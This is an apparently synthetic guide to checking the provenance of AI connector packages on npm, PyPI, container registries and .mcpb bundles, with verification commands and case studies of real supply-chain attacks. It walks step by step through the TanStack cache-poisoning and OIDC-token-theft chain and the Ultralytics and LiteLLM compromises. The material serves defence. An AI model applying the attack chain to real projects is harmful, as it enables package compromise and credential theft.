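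That last check makes impersonation slightly harder. Someone who steals Ternmail's token and builds the connector in another repository must also change the `repository` line, or npm will reject the provenance. Nothing stops them from changing it, but users can see the new value on the package's page.

The other requirements exclude some honest authors:

| How the author publishes | Trusted publishing | Provenance |
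|---|---|---|
| From a public repository, on a machine that GitHub or GitLab.com hosts | Yes | Automatic |
| The same, but with a stored token | No | Only if the author asks for it |
| From a private repository, on such a machine | Yes | No |
| Through CircleCI, another build service | Yes | No |
| On the author's own build machine or laptop | No | No |

Private repositories probably matter most for connectors. A company may offer a free connector to its paid service but keep the source code private. Its package will then have no provenance, even if the company uses trusted publishing and follows every recommendation for maintainers. The first version of a connector may also lack provenance, because the package has to exist on npm before its owner can add a trusted publishing entry.

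Authors can also turn provenance off with one line in `package.json`. A missing attestation therefore has several innocent explanations, and the user can often rule some out by checking where the project keeps its source and how it builds its releases.

### How Microsoft's Aspire tool checks provenance

Since npm doesn't compare a package's provenance with an expected repository, a program that installs npm packages has to do so itself. The command-line tool of Aspire, Microsoft's toolkit for building applications from several services, does this in *SigstoreNpmProvenanceChecker.cs*. The calling code supplies the package's name and version, and the expected repository, workflow file and build type. It can also supply the package's digest and a rule for acceptable git refs.

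The checker downloads the attestations from the same npm address as the `curl` command above and selects the SLSA provenance. It passes the bundle to a Sigstore library, then compares the individual fields. It returns a named result for each failure.

| What it compares | Where the value comes from | Result if it doesn't match |
|---|---|---|
| Package digest, if the caller supplies one | Signed statement | `AttestationParseFailed` |
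| Signing identity, which must belong to the expected GitHub repository | Certificate | `AttestationParseFailed` |
| Source repository | Certificate, or the statement if the certificate lacks it | `SourceRepositoryMismatch` |
| Workflow file | Statement | `WorkflowMismatch` |
| Build type | Statement | `BuildTypeMismatch` |
| Git ref, if the caller supplies a rule | Certificate, or the statement if the certificate lacks it | `WorkflowRefMismatch` |

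For Ternmail's connector, the caller would supply the repository `https://github.com/ternmail/connector`, the workflow `.github/workflows/publish.yml`, the GitHub Actions build type and a rule that accepts only the tag `v1.4.2`. The checker would reject the malicious release that npm accepted from the `fix-timeouts` branch. Without a rule for refs, the checker would accept that release too.

The digest is optional in the same way. If the caller leaves it out, the checker confirms that the provenance is genuine but not that it belongs to the downloaded file. Under SLSA, verifiers should also compare the `builder.id` field with an expected value, but the checker only reads it. npm's rule against self-hosted machines makes the missing check less serious.

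Some of the result names are misleading. A package from the wrong repository usually fails the signing identity check, so the checker returns `AttestationParseFailed`, as it does for a damaged file. The reason appears only in the log. If npm has no attestations for a package and answers with an error, the checker returns `AttestationFetchFailed`, which a network fault can also cause. A program that requires `Verified` is safe because it rejects all of these results, but one that retries or ignores "fetch" errors could let an unattested package through.

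The checker handles one package at a time, and only packages from GitHub. It would probably reject a release signed by Buildguild's shared workflow, because the signing identity would belong to Buildguild's repository. These limits are reasonable for a tool that installs a few packages whose origin its developers already know. An AI application could check connectors the same way, but someone would have to supply the expected values for each connector and decide how to treat its dependencies.

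## Checking a connector published on PyPI

Suppose Ternmail's `publish.yml` also builds a Python version of the connector and uploads it to PyPI as `ternmail-connector`. Ana has the same questions about this package as about the npm one. The signatures again come from Sigstore, but PyPI stores them differently, and its basic attestation contains almost nothing about the build.

### How attestations reach PyPI and its users

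PyPI used to let developers upload PGP signatures, which depend on long-lived keys. It stopped in May 2023, after an investigation found that nobody could meaningfully verify most of them. Woodruff, Tuesca and Ingram (2024), in *PEP 740*, set out the replacement. (A PEP is one of the numbered proposals through which the Python community agrees on standards.)

When Ternmail's workflow uploads a file, it sends the attestations in the same request. PyPI verifies each one and rejects the upload if any fails. It also rejects attestations from anyone except the project's trusted publishers, according to PyPI's *Producing attestations*. A project that uploads only with a stored token therefore can't have attestations. Projects that use trusted publishing on GitHub get them automatically if they upload with the official publishing action, a ready-made workflow step. GitLab projects have to add a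 signing job themselves.

Each attestation covers one file. A Python release usually consists of a source archive and one or more wheels, which are ready-to-install packages. For example, ONNX, a project that maintains a format for AI models, has a wheel called `onnx-1.20.1-cp313-cp313t-win_amd64.whl`, whose name gives the Python version and operating system it suits. One file in a release can have an attestation while another has none, so Ana has to check the file whose digest she recorded.

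PyPI collects a file's attestations in a JSON document called the provenance object, which also identifies the trusted publisher that signed them. Despite its name, the object may contain no build provenance. Similarly, the label "Full provenance" on PyPI's website means only that every file in the release has some attestation. PyPI's *pip* (2026), the page for Python's standard installer, has this label for version 26.3, although both files in that release have only a publish attestation.

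### Publish attestations and SLSA provenance

PyPI accepts at most two attestations per file, one of each type:

| | Publish attestation | SLSA provenance |
|---|---|---|
| What it shows | A particular trusted publisher signed this file for release | How a build produced the file, and from what source |
| Who may sign it | Only the workflow that the project registered as its trusted publisher | Any workflow in the same repository |
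| Contents, apart from the file's name and digest | None | The repository, commit, workflow and other details of the build |

On npm the registry signs the publish attestation, but on PyPI the project's own workflow does. The signed statement has an empty predicate because, as PyPI explains, the Sigstore certificate already contains everything about the publisher. Ana can therefore learn a good deal about the source even when a file has no SLSA provenance. For version 0.0.29 of pypi-attestations, PyPI's own verification tool, PyPI displays these details alongside the publish attestation:

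| Detail | Value |
|---|---|
| Repository | `pypi/pypi-attestations` |
| Commit | `fb35ffd...` |
| Tag | `refs/tags/v0.0.29` |
| Workflow | `release.yml` |
| Build machine | `github-hosted` |
| Event that started the run | `release` |

With these, Ana can make most of the comparisons she made for the npm package. She can check the repository, workflow and tag against her record, and look up the commit to see whether it is on the main branch.

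They don't prove that the workflow built the file from that commit. In PyPI's example for GitLab, one job builds the package, a second signs the files it receives and a third uploads them. A workflow could also download a finished wheel from elsewhere and sign that, and the certificate would look the same. Ana would have to read the workflow file at the named commit to rule this out.

SLSA provenance describes the build itself. PyPI accepts it from any workflow in the repository because one workflow may build a package and another publish it. Anyone who relies on SLSA provenance from PyPI should therefore check both the repository and the workflow that signed it. Martin-Jones's *Introducing PyPI digital attestation support* reports that Google's website deps.dev displays both types of attestation that PyPI accepts.

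### Verifying one file

This example uses version 26.0 of `packaging`, a real library for handling Python version numbers. The first command downloads the wheel that pip would choose for the user's machine:

```
pip download --no-deps --only-binary=:all: packaging==26.0

curl -o packaging-provenance.json \
  https://pypi.org/integrity/packaging/26.0/packaging-26.0-py3-none-any.whl/provenance

jq '.attestation_bundles[].publisher' packaging-provenance.json
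```

The option `--only-binary=:all:` keeps pip from falling back on a source archive, which can run code from the package even during a download. The `curl` command fetches the provenance object through PyPI's Integrity API, whose address contains the project, the version and the exact filename. `jq` then prints the publisher:

```json
{
  "environment": "pypi",
  "kind": "GitHub",
  "repository": "pypa/packaging",
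  "workflow": "publish.yml"
}
```

This block is PyPI's unsigned summary, so reading it is not a check. The verification comes from pypi-attestations, which users can install with pip:

```
pypi-attestations verify pypi \
  --repository https://github.com/pypa/packaging \
  --provenance-file packaging-provenance.json \
  packaging-26.0-py3-none-any.whl
```

The tool compares the publisher with the repository the user expects, then verifies the wheel against the signed attestations. It can also download the wheel if the user supplies the file's address on PyPI. PyPI's *Consuming attestations* shows an example. But a local file is better for Ana, because she can run `pip hash` on it and compare the SHA-256 digest with the one in her `uv.lock`. If the digests match, she has verified the same file that uv will install.

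The repository is the only expected value in this command. If someone at Ternmail ran `publish.yml` from the branch `fix-timeouts`, the resulting package would pass. A second form of the command checks the full signing identity, including the workflow and the tag. It needs the attestation in a separate file next to the wheel, which `jq` can extract from Ternmail's provenance object:

```
jq '.attestation_bundles[0].attestations[0]' ternmail-provenance.json \
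  > ternmail_connector-1.4.2-py3-none-any.whl.publish.attestation

pypi-attestations verify attestation \
  --identity https://github.com/ternmail/connector/.github/workflows/publish.yml@refs/tags/v1.4.2 \
  ternmail_connector-1.4.2-py3-none-any.whl
```

PyPI's user documentation recommends pypi-attestations for manual checks, but the tool's description says its command-line interface is mainly for experiments and may change. A company that wants to automate these checks should use the Python library behind it instead.

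As with npm, the expected repository has to come from somewhere other than the attestation. ONNX publishes the complete command in its documentation, with `onnx/onnx` as the repository. Ternmail could do the same on its setup page.

Ana still depends on PyPI in one respect, because it could leave out a genuine attestation from `ternmail/connector`. It can't forge one without help from Sigstore or GitHub. Woodruff and colleagues say their standard neither increases nor decreases users' trust in the registry.

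### What pip, uv and uvx check

As of December 2026, pip, uv and uvx do not appear to verify attestations when they install a package. PEP 740 doesn't require them to. When PyPI introduced attestations in 2024, Trail of Bits, which helped design them, called this verification "notably missing" in *Attestations* and mentioned plans for plugins that would add it to pip.

The evidence since then is indirect. The *Announcement* (2026) of pip 26.2 by the Python Packaging Authority (PyPA), which maintains pip, lists no such check among its highlights. The August 2026 release notes in Astral's *uv 0.12.5* don't mention one either. uv has uploaded attestations since November 2025, according to its *Changelog* (2025), but that helps developers who publish packages rather than users who install them. The pip highlights may have omitted a check, or pip 26.3, released in November 2026, may have added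 one. Still, Ana should assume that `uvx ternmail-connector` runs the package without checking who published it.

Python developers have discussed several ways to change this. *Ideas for client side package provenance checks* describes a syntax in which users would write `package-name from expected-source` to specify which publisher the installer should accept.

For now, the check has to be a separate step before installation. The developer of a third-party checking tool on PyPI warns that pip may then install a slightly different set of packages from the one the tool checked. Installing from a lock file with digests prevents this. Ana's `uv.lock` already records digests, and pip 26.1 introduced experimental support for a standard lock file format called `pylock.toml`, according to PyPA's *Announcement* of the release.

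### Recording the expected publisher in pylock.toml

`pylock.toml` can hold the same versions and digests as other lock files. It also has a place for the publisher of each package. The entry for Ternmail's connector could include these lines:

```toml
name = "ternmail-connector"
version = "1.4.2"
attestation-identities = [
  { kind = "GitHub", repository = "ternmail/connector", workflow = "publish.yml" },
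]
```

Brett Cannon, who wrote the pylock.toml standard, explains in *Why pylock.toml includes digital attestations* (2026) that a program can compare the recorded publisher with the one PyPI reports for the same file. A difference suggests that something is wrong. People reviewing changes to a lock file can also spot a problem, for instance if the publisher's details disappear between two versions.

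For a version already in the lock file, checking the digest gives better protection than checking the publisher's details. Those details are more useful during an update, when the digest changes but the publisher should stay the same. A program that only compares them with PyPI's summary has to trust PyPI, so it should also verify the attestation.

Lock files may not include the publisher details at all. The Python Developer Tooling Handbook's *How to publish Python packages with digital attestations* says lock file tools fetch them from PyPI automatically. But one user who replied to Cannon's Mastodon post in March 2026 had tried uv, pip and the package manager pdm, and found no publisher information in any of the lock files. That is one person's experience, and the tools may have changed since. Ana can search her own lock file for `attestation-identities` and, if it isn't there, record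 the expected publisher herself.

### Ultralytics: two attacks on one project

In December 2024 an attacker published four malicious versions of `ultralytics`, a popular Python package for image recognition. The project used trusted publishing and produced attestations, so the incident shows how useful PyPI's evidence was in a real attack.

| Version | Published (UTC) | How it reached PyPI | Publish attestation | Result of a check for the official repository |
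|---|---|---|---|---|
| 8.3.41 | 4 December, 20:51 | The project's own workflow | Valid | Pass |
| 8.3.42 | 5 December, 12:47 | The project's own workflow | Valid | Pass |
| 8.3.45 | 7 December, 01:41 | A leftover API token | None | Fail |
| 8.3.46 | 7 December | A leftover API token | None | Fail |

For the first two versions, the attacker tampered with the cache that the project's build workflow used. The workflow then built, signed and published the malicious package as usual. Every statement in the attestation was true, so a user who checked the repository and workflow would have accepted the package. According to ReversingLabs, the malicious code entered after the project's code review, so reading the source code might not have helped. A user could have found the malicious code by comparing the package's files with the commit named in the certificate, but few users do that.

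The maintainers had trouble finding the cause too. They released 8.3.42 as the safe replacement for 8.3.41, but it contained the same malicious code. A clean version, 8.3.43, followed later that day. Snyk's *Ultralytics AI Pwn Request Supply Chain Attack* (2024) reports that 8.3.41 was available for about twelve hours and 8.3.42 for one.

The attestations did not stop this part of the attack, but they helped investigators. According to PyPI's *Supply-chain attack analysis* (2024), the attestations and Sigstore's log showed that the releases had come through the official workflow, not from a stolen token. The malicious code therefore had to be in the repository or enter during the build, which narrowed the search. Socket reports that a Trail of Bits employee also cited the valid attestations as evidence that the project's build setup was at fault, not PyPI.

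Two days later the attacker used a PyPI token that the workflow could still access. PyPI thinks the token may have been left over from before the project adopted trusted publishing. The attacker uploaded 8.3.45 and 8.3.46 directly, so neither had an attestation or matching activity in the repository. An installer that required an attestation from the official workflow would have refused both, but no common installer required one. Version 8.3.45 remained available for about eight hours.

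Ternmail could have prevented an attack like the second one by revoking its old tokens when it switched to trusted publishing. After the incident, PyPI suggested that it could help projects notice tokens they no longer use.

### LiteLLM and Telnyx: no earlier attestations to compare

LiteLLM is a Python library for using AI models from many providers, so a connector might well depend on it. On 24 March 2026, attackers published two malicious versions of it, 1.82.7 and 1.82.8. Three days later, according to Datadog Security Labs, they published two malicious versions of `telnyx`, a library for telephone services, numbered 4.87.1 and 4.87.2.

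The attack began with Trivy, a security scanner that many projects run in their build workflows. Akamai reports that a group called TeamPCP used a stolen access token to point 76 of the 77 version tags of Trivy's GitHub action to malicious code. Any workflow that ran the action could then leak its secrets. PyPI's *Incident Report* (2026) traces the malicious LiteLLM and Telnyx releases to an API token exposed this way. The malware in those releases collected more passwords and keys, which the attackers could use against other projects.

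PyPI quarantined the LiteLLM versions 2 hours and 32 minutes after the first upload. By then they had more than 119,000 downloads, or about 780 a minute. Comparing this with LiteLLM's normal rate of around 1,700 installations a minute, PyPI estimates that 40 to 50 percent of installations had no pinned version and took the newest release. The Telnyx versions were available for 3 hours and 42 minutes.

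Two days after the LiteLLM attack, Cannon argued on Mastodon that attestations and `pylock.toml` would have helped, because the malicious versions would have lacked the usual publisher details and people reviewing their lock files would have noticed. Cannon's article states that this would have required the project to already be using trusted publishing with attestations.

Comparing a release's attestations with those of the previous version could not have protected users in March 2026. PyPI says that both projects adopted trusted publishing after the attacks, and since PyPI accepts attestations only from trusted publishers, their earlier releases can't have had any. A user who compared LiteLLM 1.82.7 with the previous version would have found no attestation for either release. Cannon's argument is still sound as advice to maintainers.

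Another commenter objected to Cannon's post, believing that the attackers had committed the malicious code to LiteLLM's repository, in which case trusted publishing would have produced a release with a valid attestation. PyPI instead reported an exposed token, but the first half of the Ultralytics attack shows that a malicious release can have a valid attestation.

Trusted publishing might also have helped more directly, because the infected scanner would have had no stored PyPI token to steal if the project had also removed its old ones. But if the scanner ran in the same job that publishes the package, it could probably have requested a new short-lived token.

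A lock file from the previous week would have protected someone installing a connector that depended on LiteLLM from the malicious versions, with or without attestations. A cooldown on new releases would have worked too, because the malicious LiteLLM and Telnyx versions were each up for less than four hours. PyPI recommends a three-day cooldown, which users can set with `exclude-newer = "P3D"` in uv's global configuration file.

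## Checking connectors shipped as container images or bundles

Running Ternmail's connector from npm or PyPI takes developer tools and a hand-edited configuration file. Anthropic's *Desktop Extensions* reports that many Claude Desktop users found this too hard or got stuck on dependencies, and it introduces bundles as the remedy. A bundle is a ZIP archive with the extension `.mcpb` that holds the connector, its dependencies and a manifest describing it. The desktop application installs it in one step. A container image also includes parts of an operating system. A program such as Docker runs it separately from the rest of the machine, which is another reason to choose an image.

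Both formats make pinning easier because one digest covers the connector and everything shipped with it, so Ana doesn't need a lock file for a hundred packages. However, the archive's builder chose the versions of those packages, and Ana gets a security fix in one of them only when the builder makes a new archive.

### Pinning and verifying an image

Suppose Ternmail's `publish.yml` also publishes an image called `ghcr.io/ternmail/connector:1.4.2` on GitHub's container registry. Here `1.4.2` is a tag, which the publisher can move to a different image, unlike an npm version number, which nobody can reuse. Data Sharing Framework's *Verify Image Signature* therefore tells users to include the digest both when they check an image and when they run it. The MCP Registry accepts either a tag or a digest in its image entries, according to Model Context Protocol.

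This command prints the digest without starting the image:

```
docker buildx imagetools inspect ghcr.io/ternmail/connector:1.4.2
```

If the image supports several types of processor, the first digest belongs to an index that lists one image for each type. Ana should record that one, because publishers often sign only the index. She can then check the signature:

```
cosign verify \
  --certificate-identity="https://github.com/ternmail/connector/.github/workflows/publish.yml@refs/tags/v1.4.2" \
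  --certificate-oidc-issuer="https://token.actions.githubusercontent.com" \
  ghcr.io/ternmail/connector@sha256:5be0...
```

If the check succeeds, Cosign prints the verified claims and exits with status 0. An attestation is a separate record and needs its own command. For provenance that Ternmail made with GitHub's attestation service, it would be:

```
gh attestation verify oci://ghcr.io/ternmail/connector@sha256:5be0... \
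  --repo ternmail/connector --source-ref refs/tags/v1.4.2
```

The configuration should contain the same digest, or the tag could move between the check and the first start:

```json
{
  "mcpServers": {
    "mail": {
      "command": "docker",
      "args": ["run", "-i", "--rm", "ghcr.io/ternmail/connector@sha256:5be0..."]
    }
  }
}
```

With this configuration, Docker rejects a download that doesn't match the digest. Docker doesn't check the signature again, so the protection depends on Ana having checked it.

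A company can make the check compulsory by putting it in the software that starts the image. Red Hat's *Verifying container signatures for supply chain security* describes how to do this in MicroShift, its small platform for running containers. An administrator gives the container runtime a public key, and the runtime checks each image against it. Kyverno and Sigstore's policy controller do a similar job for Kubernetes clusters, but most people who run a connector on a laptop have neither.

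### What ToolHive expects of GitHub's connector

Stacklok's ToolHive, a program that runs connectors in containers, does this kind of check on a single machine. For connectors in its built-in registry, it looks up the image's signatures and attestations and compares them with values that Stacklok recorded in advance. Ana therefore doesn't have to find the expected repository herself, but she must trust that Stacklok found the right one.

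Stacklok published the values for the connector that gives agents access to GitHub:

| Field | Expected value | What it excludes |
|---|---|---|
| `sigstore_url` | `tuf-repo-cdn.sigstore.dev` | Certificates from a private copy of Sigstore |
| `repository_uri` | `https://github.com/github/github-mcp-server` | Images from forks and lookalike repositories |
| `signer_identity` | `/.github/workflows/docker-publish.yml` | Images signed by another workflow in the same repository, such as one for tests |
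| `runner_environment` | `github-hosted` | Builds on a machine that the project runs itself |
| `cert_issuer` | `https://token.actions.githubusercontent.com` | Identities that another service confirmed, such as a personal Google account |

The address in the last field belongs to the GitHub service that issues OIDC tokens. For a public project, Sigstore's Fulcio issues the certificate, so Stacklok is slightly wrong to describe the field as proof that GitHub's certificate authority signed the image.

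None of the five fields contains a git ref, a commit or a digest. An image built by running `docker-publish.yml` from an unreviewed branch would therefore match all five, and so would an old release with a known security hole. A user who wants to exclude these cases has to pin the digest as well.

The default setting is also lenient. ToolHive has three levels of verification, and the default, `warn`, reports a failed check but starts the connector anyway. This command makes a failure block it:

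```
thv run --image-verification=enabled github
```

According to Stacklok's *ToolHive registry JSON schema*, the company now treats its original format for registry entries as legacy and also supports the official MCP Registry's format. The expectations remain after the change, and a later example in Stacklok's documentation, for a connector that looks up known vulnerabilities, has the same five fields.

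### Which attestations images, npm and PyPI can carry

Osorio, the creator of ToolHive, argues for distributing connectors as container images, partly because a container registry can store more kinds of evidence. His 2026 conference slides, *OCI Images as MCP Packaging*, compare images with npm and PyPI. OCI, the Open Container Initiative, maintains the standard for images. The table below corrects several of the slides' entries using documentation from the registries and Sigstore.

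| Signed evidence | Container image | npm package | PyPI file |
|---|---|---|---|
| Build provenance | Yes | Yes, from GitHub Actions or GitLab | Yes, as an optional second attestation |
| Publish attestation | Possible, but not customary | Yes, signed by npm | Yes, signed by the project's workflow |
| List of components | Yes | No | No |
| Other types of attestation | Any | No | No |

npm returns a publish attestation alongside build provenance, as Sigstore's worked example shows, and PyPI accepts SLSA provenance as well as publish attestations. The slides list only build provenance for npm and only publish attestations for PyPI, with GitHub Actions as the only source of npm's provenance. They also list no enforcement for npm packages, omitting pnpm's option to block a version with weaker evidence than earlier ones.

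Osorio is right about the list of components, usually called a software bill of materials (SBOM). Neither npm nor PyPI accepts one as an attestation. Ternmail could still sign an SBOM for its npm package through GitHub's attestation service, which works for any file built in GitHub Actions, though users would have to fetch the signed SBOM from GitHub.

An SBOM is particularly useful for an image because much of the image is software other than the connector. In an example from Docker's documentation, the attested SBOM for one image lists 101 packages. `npm audit` would find known vulnerabilities only in the connector's JavaScript dependencies, while an image scanner also covers the operating system's packages. Some of that extra coverage is needed only because the image includes packages that the npm version of the connector would not have installed.

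The table also shows only what each format allows. An image on a container registry may have no signature or attestation whatsoever.

### When someone else builds the image

Many connectors exist only as npm or PyPI packages, so other organisations turn them into images. Stacklok does this in a project called Dockyard. One of its images contains version 2.1.0 of `context7`, an npm package. These lines, adapted from the command that Stacklok recommends, check it:

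```
REPO="https://github.com/stacklok/dockyard"

cosign verify \
  --certificate-oidc-issuer="https://token.actions.githubusercontent.com" \
  --certificate-identity-regexp="^$REPO/.github/workflows/build-containers.yml@refs/heads/" \
  ghcr.io/stacklok/dockyard/npx/context7:2.1.0
```

The expected identity is Stacklok's workflow, not the package developers' workflow. A successful result therefore shows that Dockyard built the image, but not who built the npm package inside it.

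This matters if the package was malicious before it was repackaged. Suppose a thief uses a stolen token to upload version 1.4.3 of Ternmail's connector to npm, and a repackager's workflow downloads it the same night. The npm package has no provenance, which might have made Ana suspicious, but the image has a valid signature from a well-known company and accurate provenance for the repackaging.

Ana therefore verifies the image against the repackager's identity, then verifies the npm package against `ternmail/connector`, as she would when installing it directly. To confirm that the image contains that package, she can use `docker create` and `docker cp` to copy the connector's folder out of the image without starting a container, then compare the files with those in the package from npm. She can't use npm's digest instead, because it covers only the compressed package. She also needs to check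 the dependencies, since the repackager may have installed different versions from those in her lock file.

Docker builds some of the images in its connector catalogue itself, from source code rather than from the developer's npm or PyPI release. Docker (2025) announced in December 2025 that each catalogue entry must name an exact commit. Docker copies the commit's identifier into a label on the image. A stolen npm token would not affect such an image unless one of the build's dependencies was published with that token.

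Docker signs these images with its own long-lived key, so users verify them with Cosign's `--key` option and Docker's published public key. There is no workflow identity to compare. The signature shows that Docker approved the image, and the label shows which commit Docker says it used. Ana can look up that commit in Ternmail's repository, but she has to trust Docker that the image was built from it.

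Connectors in the catalogue also undergo code review. An automated workflow looks for new commits every night and proposes an update for each connector that has changed. Two AI agents, Claude Code and OpenAI Codex, then review the changes. A critical finding blocks the update, while findings of high or medium risk only produce warnings. The code could contain instructions aimed at the agents, so Docker gives the agents read-only access to it and runs them without internet access or secrets.

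At the time of the announcement, Docker staff still read the reports, but the company planned to approve most updates automatically once it had tuned the system. The agents had found logic errors with security consequences but nothing malicious. That is encouraging about the catalogue's contents, but it doesn't show how reliably the agents would detect a deliberate backdoor. The catalogue's "known publisher" icon shows only where a connector comes from.

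### What a bundle's digest proves

If Ternmail published a bundle, its MCP Registry entry would include the required SHA-256 digest in this form:

```json
{
  "registryType": "mcpb",
  "identifier": "https://github.com/ternmail/connector/releases/download/v1.4.2/ternmail-mcp.mcpb",
  "fileSha256": "b71e...",
  "transport": { "type": "stdio" }
}
```

The application that installs the bundle checks this digest, according to Model Context Protocol, but the registry does not. The installation would therefore fail if someone replaced the file on Ternmail's release page. A user who downloads the file in a browser has to run `openssl dgst -sha256 ternmail-mcp.mcpb` and compare the digests by hand.

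Like npm's digest, this digest doesn't show who built the file. It also doesn't protect against someone who takes over Ternmail's GitHub account. That account controls both the release page and the `io.github.ternmail/` entries, so the intruder could publish a malicious version 1.4.3 with a correct digest.

Provenance can fill part of this gap. Bundles for the registry have to be on GitHub's or GitLab's release pages, and a project that builds its bundle in GitHub Actions can attest it like any other file. Ana would then run:

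```
gh attestation verify ternmail-mcp.mcpb \
  --repo ternmail/connector --source-ref refs/tags/v1.4.2
```

The registry doesn't require this attestation, so many bundles may not have one.

### Why bundle signatures are of little use so far

Bundles also have their own signing system, which doesn't use Sigstore. `mcpb sign` adds a signature made with an ordinary certificate and a key that the developer keeps. Anthropic's *Desktop extensions* lists signing and verification among the format's features, but verification has not worked properly.

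The matching command, `mcpb verify`, reported every signed bundle as unsigned. In *fix*, a code change proposed in March 2026, bryan-anthropic explained that the command relied on an unwritten library function that always returned an error. bryan-anthropic closed the proposal in favour of another developer's version, but a commit from June 2026 still described the fault. Publishers have had to work around it. StackQL, which distributes a connector as bundles, treats the command's result as advisory and checks only that the file has a signature block. Its release process signs bundles if a certificate is available and otherwise publishes them unsigned.

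On an affected version, "not signed" therefore reveals nothing about the bundle. At least the fault doesn't make forged signatures look valid.

When companies signed bundles with their own signing systems, those systems added the signature to the end of the ZIP archive without updating a field that records the length of the extra data. Claude Desktop then rejected the bundle as damaged, according to a second proposal by bryan-anthropic. Signing also changes the file's digest, so a publisher has to calculate the digest for the registry after signing.

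Even with a working verifier, Ana would have to decide whether to trust the signature. In the proposed fix, a successful check can print "Signature is valid (self-signed)" and the publisher's name. Anyone can create a self-signed certificate with any name in it, so she would have to compare the certificate's fingerprint with one from Ternmail's website.

An attacker can also remove the signature. The tool's `mcpb unsign` command does this, and NuGet's *Mcpb.Cli 0.3.5* lists it for the .NET version. Signatures can stop altered bundles only if the application refuses unsigned ones.

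Claude Desktop has a setting that requires bundles to be signed, `isDesktopExtensionSignatureRequired`, but it is off by default. The setting's documentation covers the version of the application for companies that use their own model provider. Anthropic's *MCP, plugins, skills, and hooks* says the setting blocks the installation of unsigned bundles, but doesn't apply to a bundle inside a plugin (a package of extra features for the application). Anthropic's *Configuration reference* says it rejects bundles without a signature from a "trusted publisher", which would presumably exclude self-signed bundles too. An administrator should test the setting with both unsigned and self-signed bundles before relying on it.

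A company can instead restrict which bundles its employees may install. Claude Desktop has an allowlist for this, but Anthropic warns that it is also off by default. Until an owner of the organisation's account turns it on, users can install anything in the extension directory.

### What Windows requires

Microsoft has proposed enforcing signing in Windows itself. *Securing the Model Context Protocol* (Microsoft, 2025) describes a planned Windows registry that would admit a connector only if its developer had signed the code and declared the privileges the connector needs. The connector would also need a package identity, which is a name that Windows can tie to an installed application, and could not change its tools while running. Microsoft said these requirements could change.

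A public preview followed in November 2025, according to Microsoft's *Ignite 2025* (2025). By default, connectors in this registry run under a separate account. Microsoft says that to qualify, a connector has to be an `.exe` program with a package identity from MSIX, Microsoft's format for installing applications. Windows normally installs an MSIX package only if it has a valid signature from a certificate the machine trusts. That signature identifies a publisher but, unlike provenance, doesn't link the package to a repository or commit.

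Microsoft's *Register an MCP server with an MCP bundle* says that agents can't reach bundles through the Windows registry by default. Users can change this with a setting called "Reduce protections for agent connectors", which Microsoft intends for testing. Microsoft says developers can avoid relying on this setting by giving the program an identity through a separate MSIX package.

Microsoft's documentation still describes all this as pre-release. The rules also apply only to connectors that an agent reaches through the Windows registry, so they don't apply if Ana's AI application starts `npx` from its own configuration file, as in Ternmail's original instructions.

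## When a malicious release carries a valid attestation

In the Ultralytics attack of 2024, a project's own workflow signed and published malware. Attackers did the same on npm in 2026, on a much larger scale, and in September one of their targets was a connector. A user who checked only that the repository's name matched the expected one would have accepted these releases. Other checks could have rejected them, but which ones depended on how the attacker got in.

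### TanStack: malware from the official release workflow

On 11 May 2026 an attacker published 84 malicious versions of 42 TanStack packages within six minutes. The uploads used TanStack's genuine trusted publishing entry, and nobody had modified the release workflow, according to OSV's *GHSA-g7cv-rxg3-hmpx* (2026). TanStack's *Postmortem* explains how this was possible:

1. The attacker copied the repository `TanStack/router` to another GitHub account and added a malicious script to the copy.
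2. On the morning of 11 May, the attacker opened a pull request, which is a proposal to merge changes into a project. TanStack had a workflow that measured how each proposal affected the size of its packages. The workflow used a trigger called `pull_request_target`, which runs in the main repository's context without waiting for a maintainer's approval. It built the proposed code and so ran the attacker's script.
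3. The script tampered with the libraries in the project's build cache. The name of a cache entry depended on a digest of the project's public lock file, so the attacker could work out which entry the release workflow would load.
4. Two minutes after GitHub saved the poisoned cache, the attacker replaced the proposal with an empty one and closed it.
5. Almost eight hours later, a maintainer merged an unrelated fix, which started the release workflow. It loaded the poisoned cache, and the malware searched the build machine's memory for an OIDC token.
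6. The malware used the token to upload packages directly to npm. A second merge started another run, with the same result.

The developer who wrote the size-measuring workflow had recognized some of the danger and intended its build job to have read-only permissions. But GitHub's cache used a separate credential that those permissions did not cover.

*TeamPCP's Mini Shai-Hulud Is Back* (Kurmi, 2026) reproduces the provenance of one of the malicious packages. The provenance lists the repository `TanStack/router`, the workflow `release.yml`, the branch `main` and a GitHub-hosted machine, as it would for a legitimate release. The source commit would presumably have passed inspection too, because a maintainer's ordinary merge started the run.

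The malware broke the project's tests, so GitHub skipped the step that normally publishes the packages and recorded both runs as failed. Even so, npm received the first malicious packages eight seconds before the first run ended and the second set six seconds before the second run ended.

Ordinary verification tools don't look at a run's outcome, as SLSA points out. Ana can look it up herself, because the provenance contains the run's address. For version 1.4.2 of Ternmail's connector, she would enter:

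```
gh run view 9000000001 --repo ternmail/connector --attempt 1 \
  --json conclusion,event,headBranch
```

The `conclusion` should be `success`. A failed run is a reason to wait and ask, since some projects publish a package and then fail at a later step, such as posting an announcement. Even a successful run proves little, because GitHub doesn't sign this result as part of the provenance and malware may not cause a failure. TanStack says it was lucky that the malware broke the tests, and a more careful attacker could have gone unnoticed for hours longer.

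The packages' contents also showed signs of tampering. Kurmi found that the malicious version of one package had 124 files, up from 101 in a clean version, and was 3.7 times as large when unpacked. It contained a 2.3 MB file that didn't belong there, `router_init.js`, and a new optional dependency that npm would fetch from GitHub. OSV's advisory recommends downloading a suspect version with `npm pack`, which doesn't run the package's install scripts, and checking it for these signs.

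The optional dependency started the malware during installation. npm 12, which arrived two months later, blocks this route by default.

Outside researchers reported the attack about half an hour after the first upload, and TanStack had no alerts of its own. TanStack couldn't withdraw most of the versions because npm doesn't let maintainers remove a package that others depend on. The malicious files stayed available until npm's security team removed them, which TanStack says added hours of delay.

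### How the worm spread to other projects

The malware, a worm called Mini Shai-Hulud, used the credentials it stole to infect other packages. By the end of the day it had reached at least 170, according to Snyk's *TanStack npm packages compromised* (2026). Kurmi's list includes `cmux-agent-mcp`, `nextmove-mcp` and `@squawk/mcp`, whose names suggest they are connectors.

Kurmi's analysis suggests that at least some of the attestations for the infected packages were genuine, although Snyk writes that the worm forged them. If the malware found an OIDC token, it used the token to get a certificate from Sigstore's Fulcio, as any signing client does. The resulting attestation would name the workflow in which the malware was running. With only a stolen npm token, the worm could publish a package but not attest it in the name of the project's workflow.

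Snyk warns that the malware installs a service called `gh-token-monitor`, which deletes the user's home directory if GitHub rejects the stolen token. Anyone who installed an affected version should therefore disable this service before revoking any tokens.

### Why the attestations were not level 3

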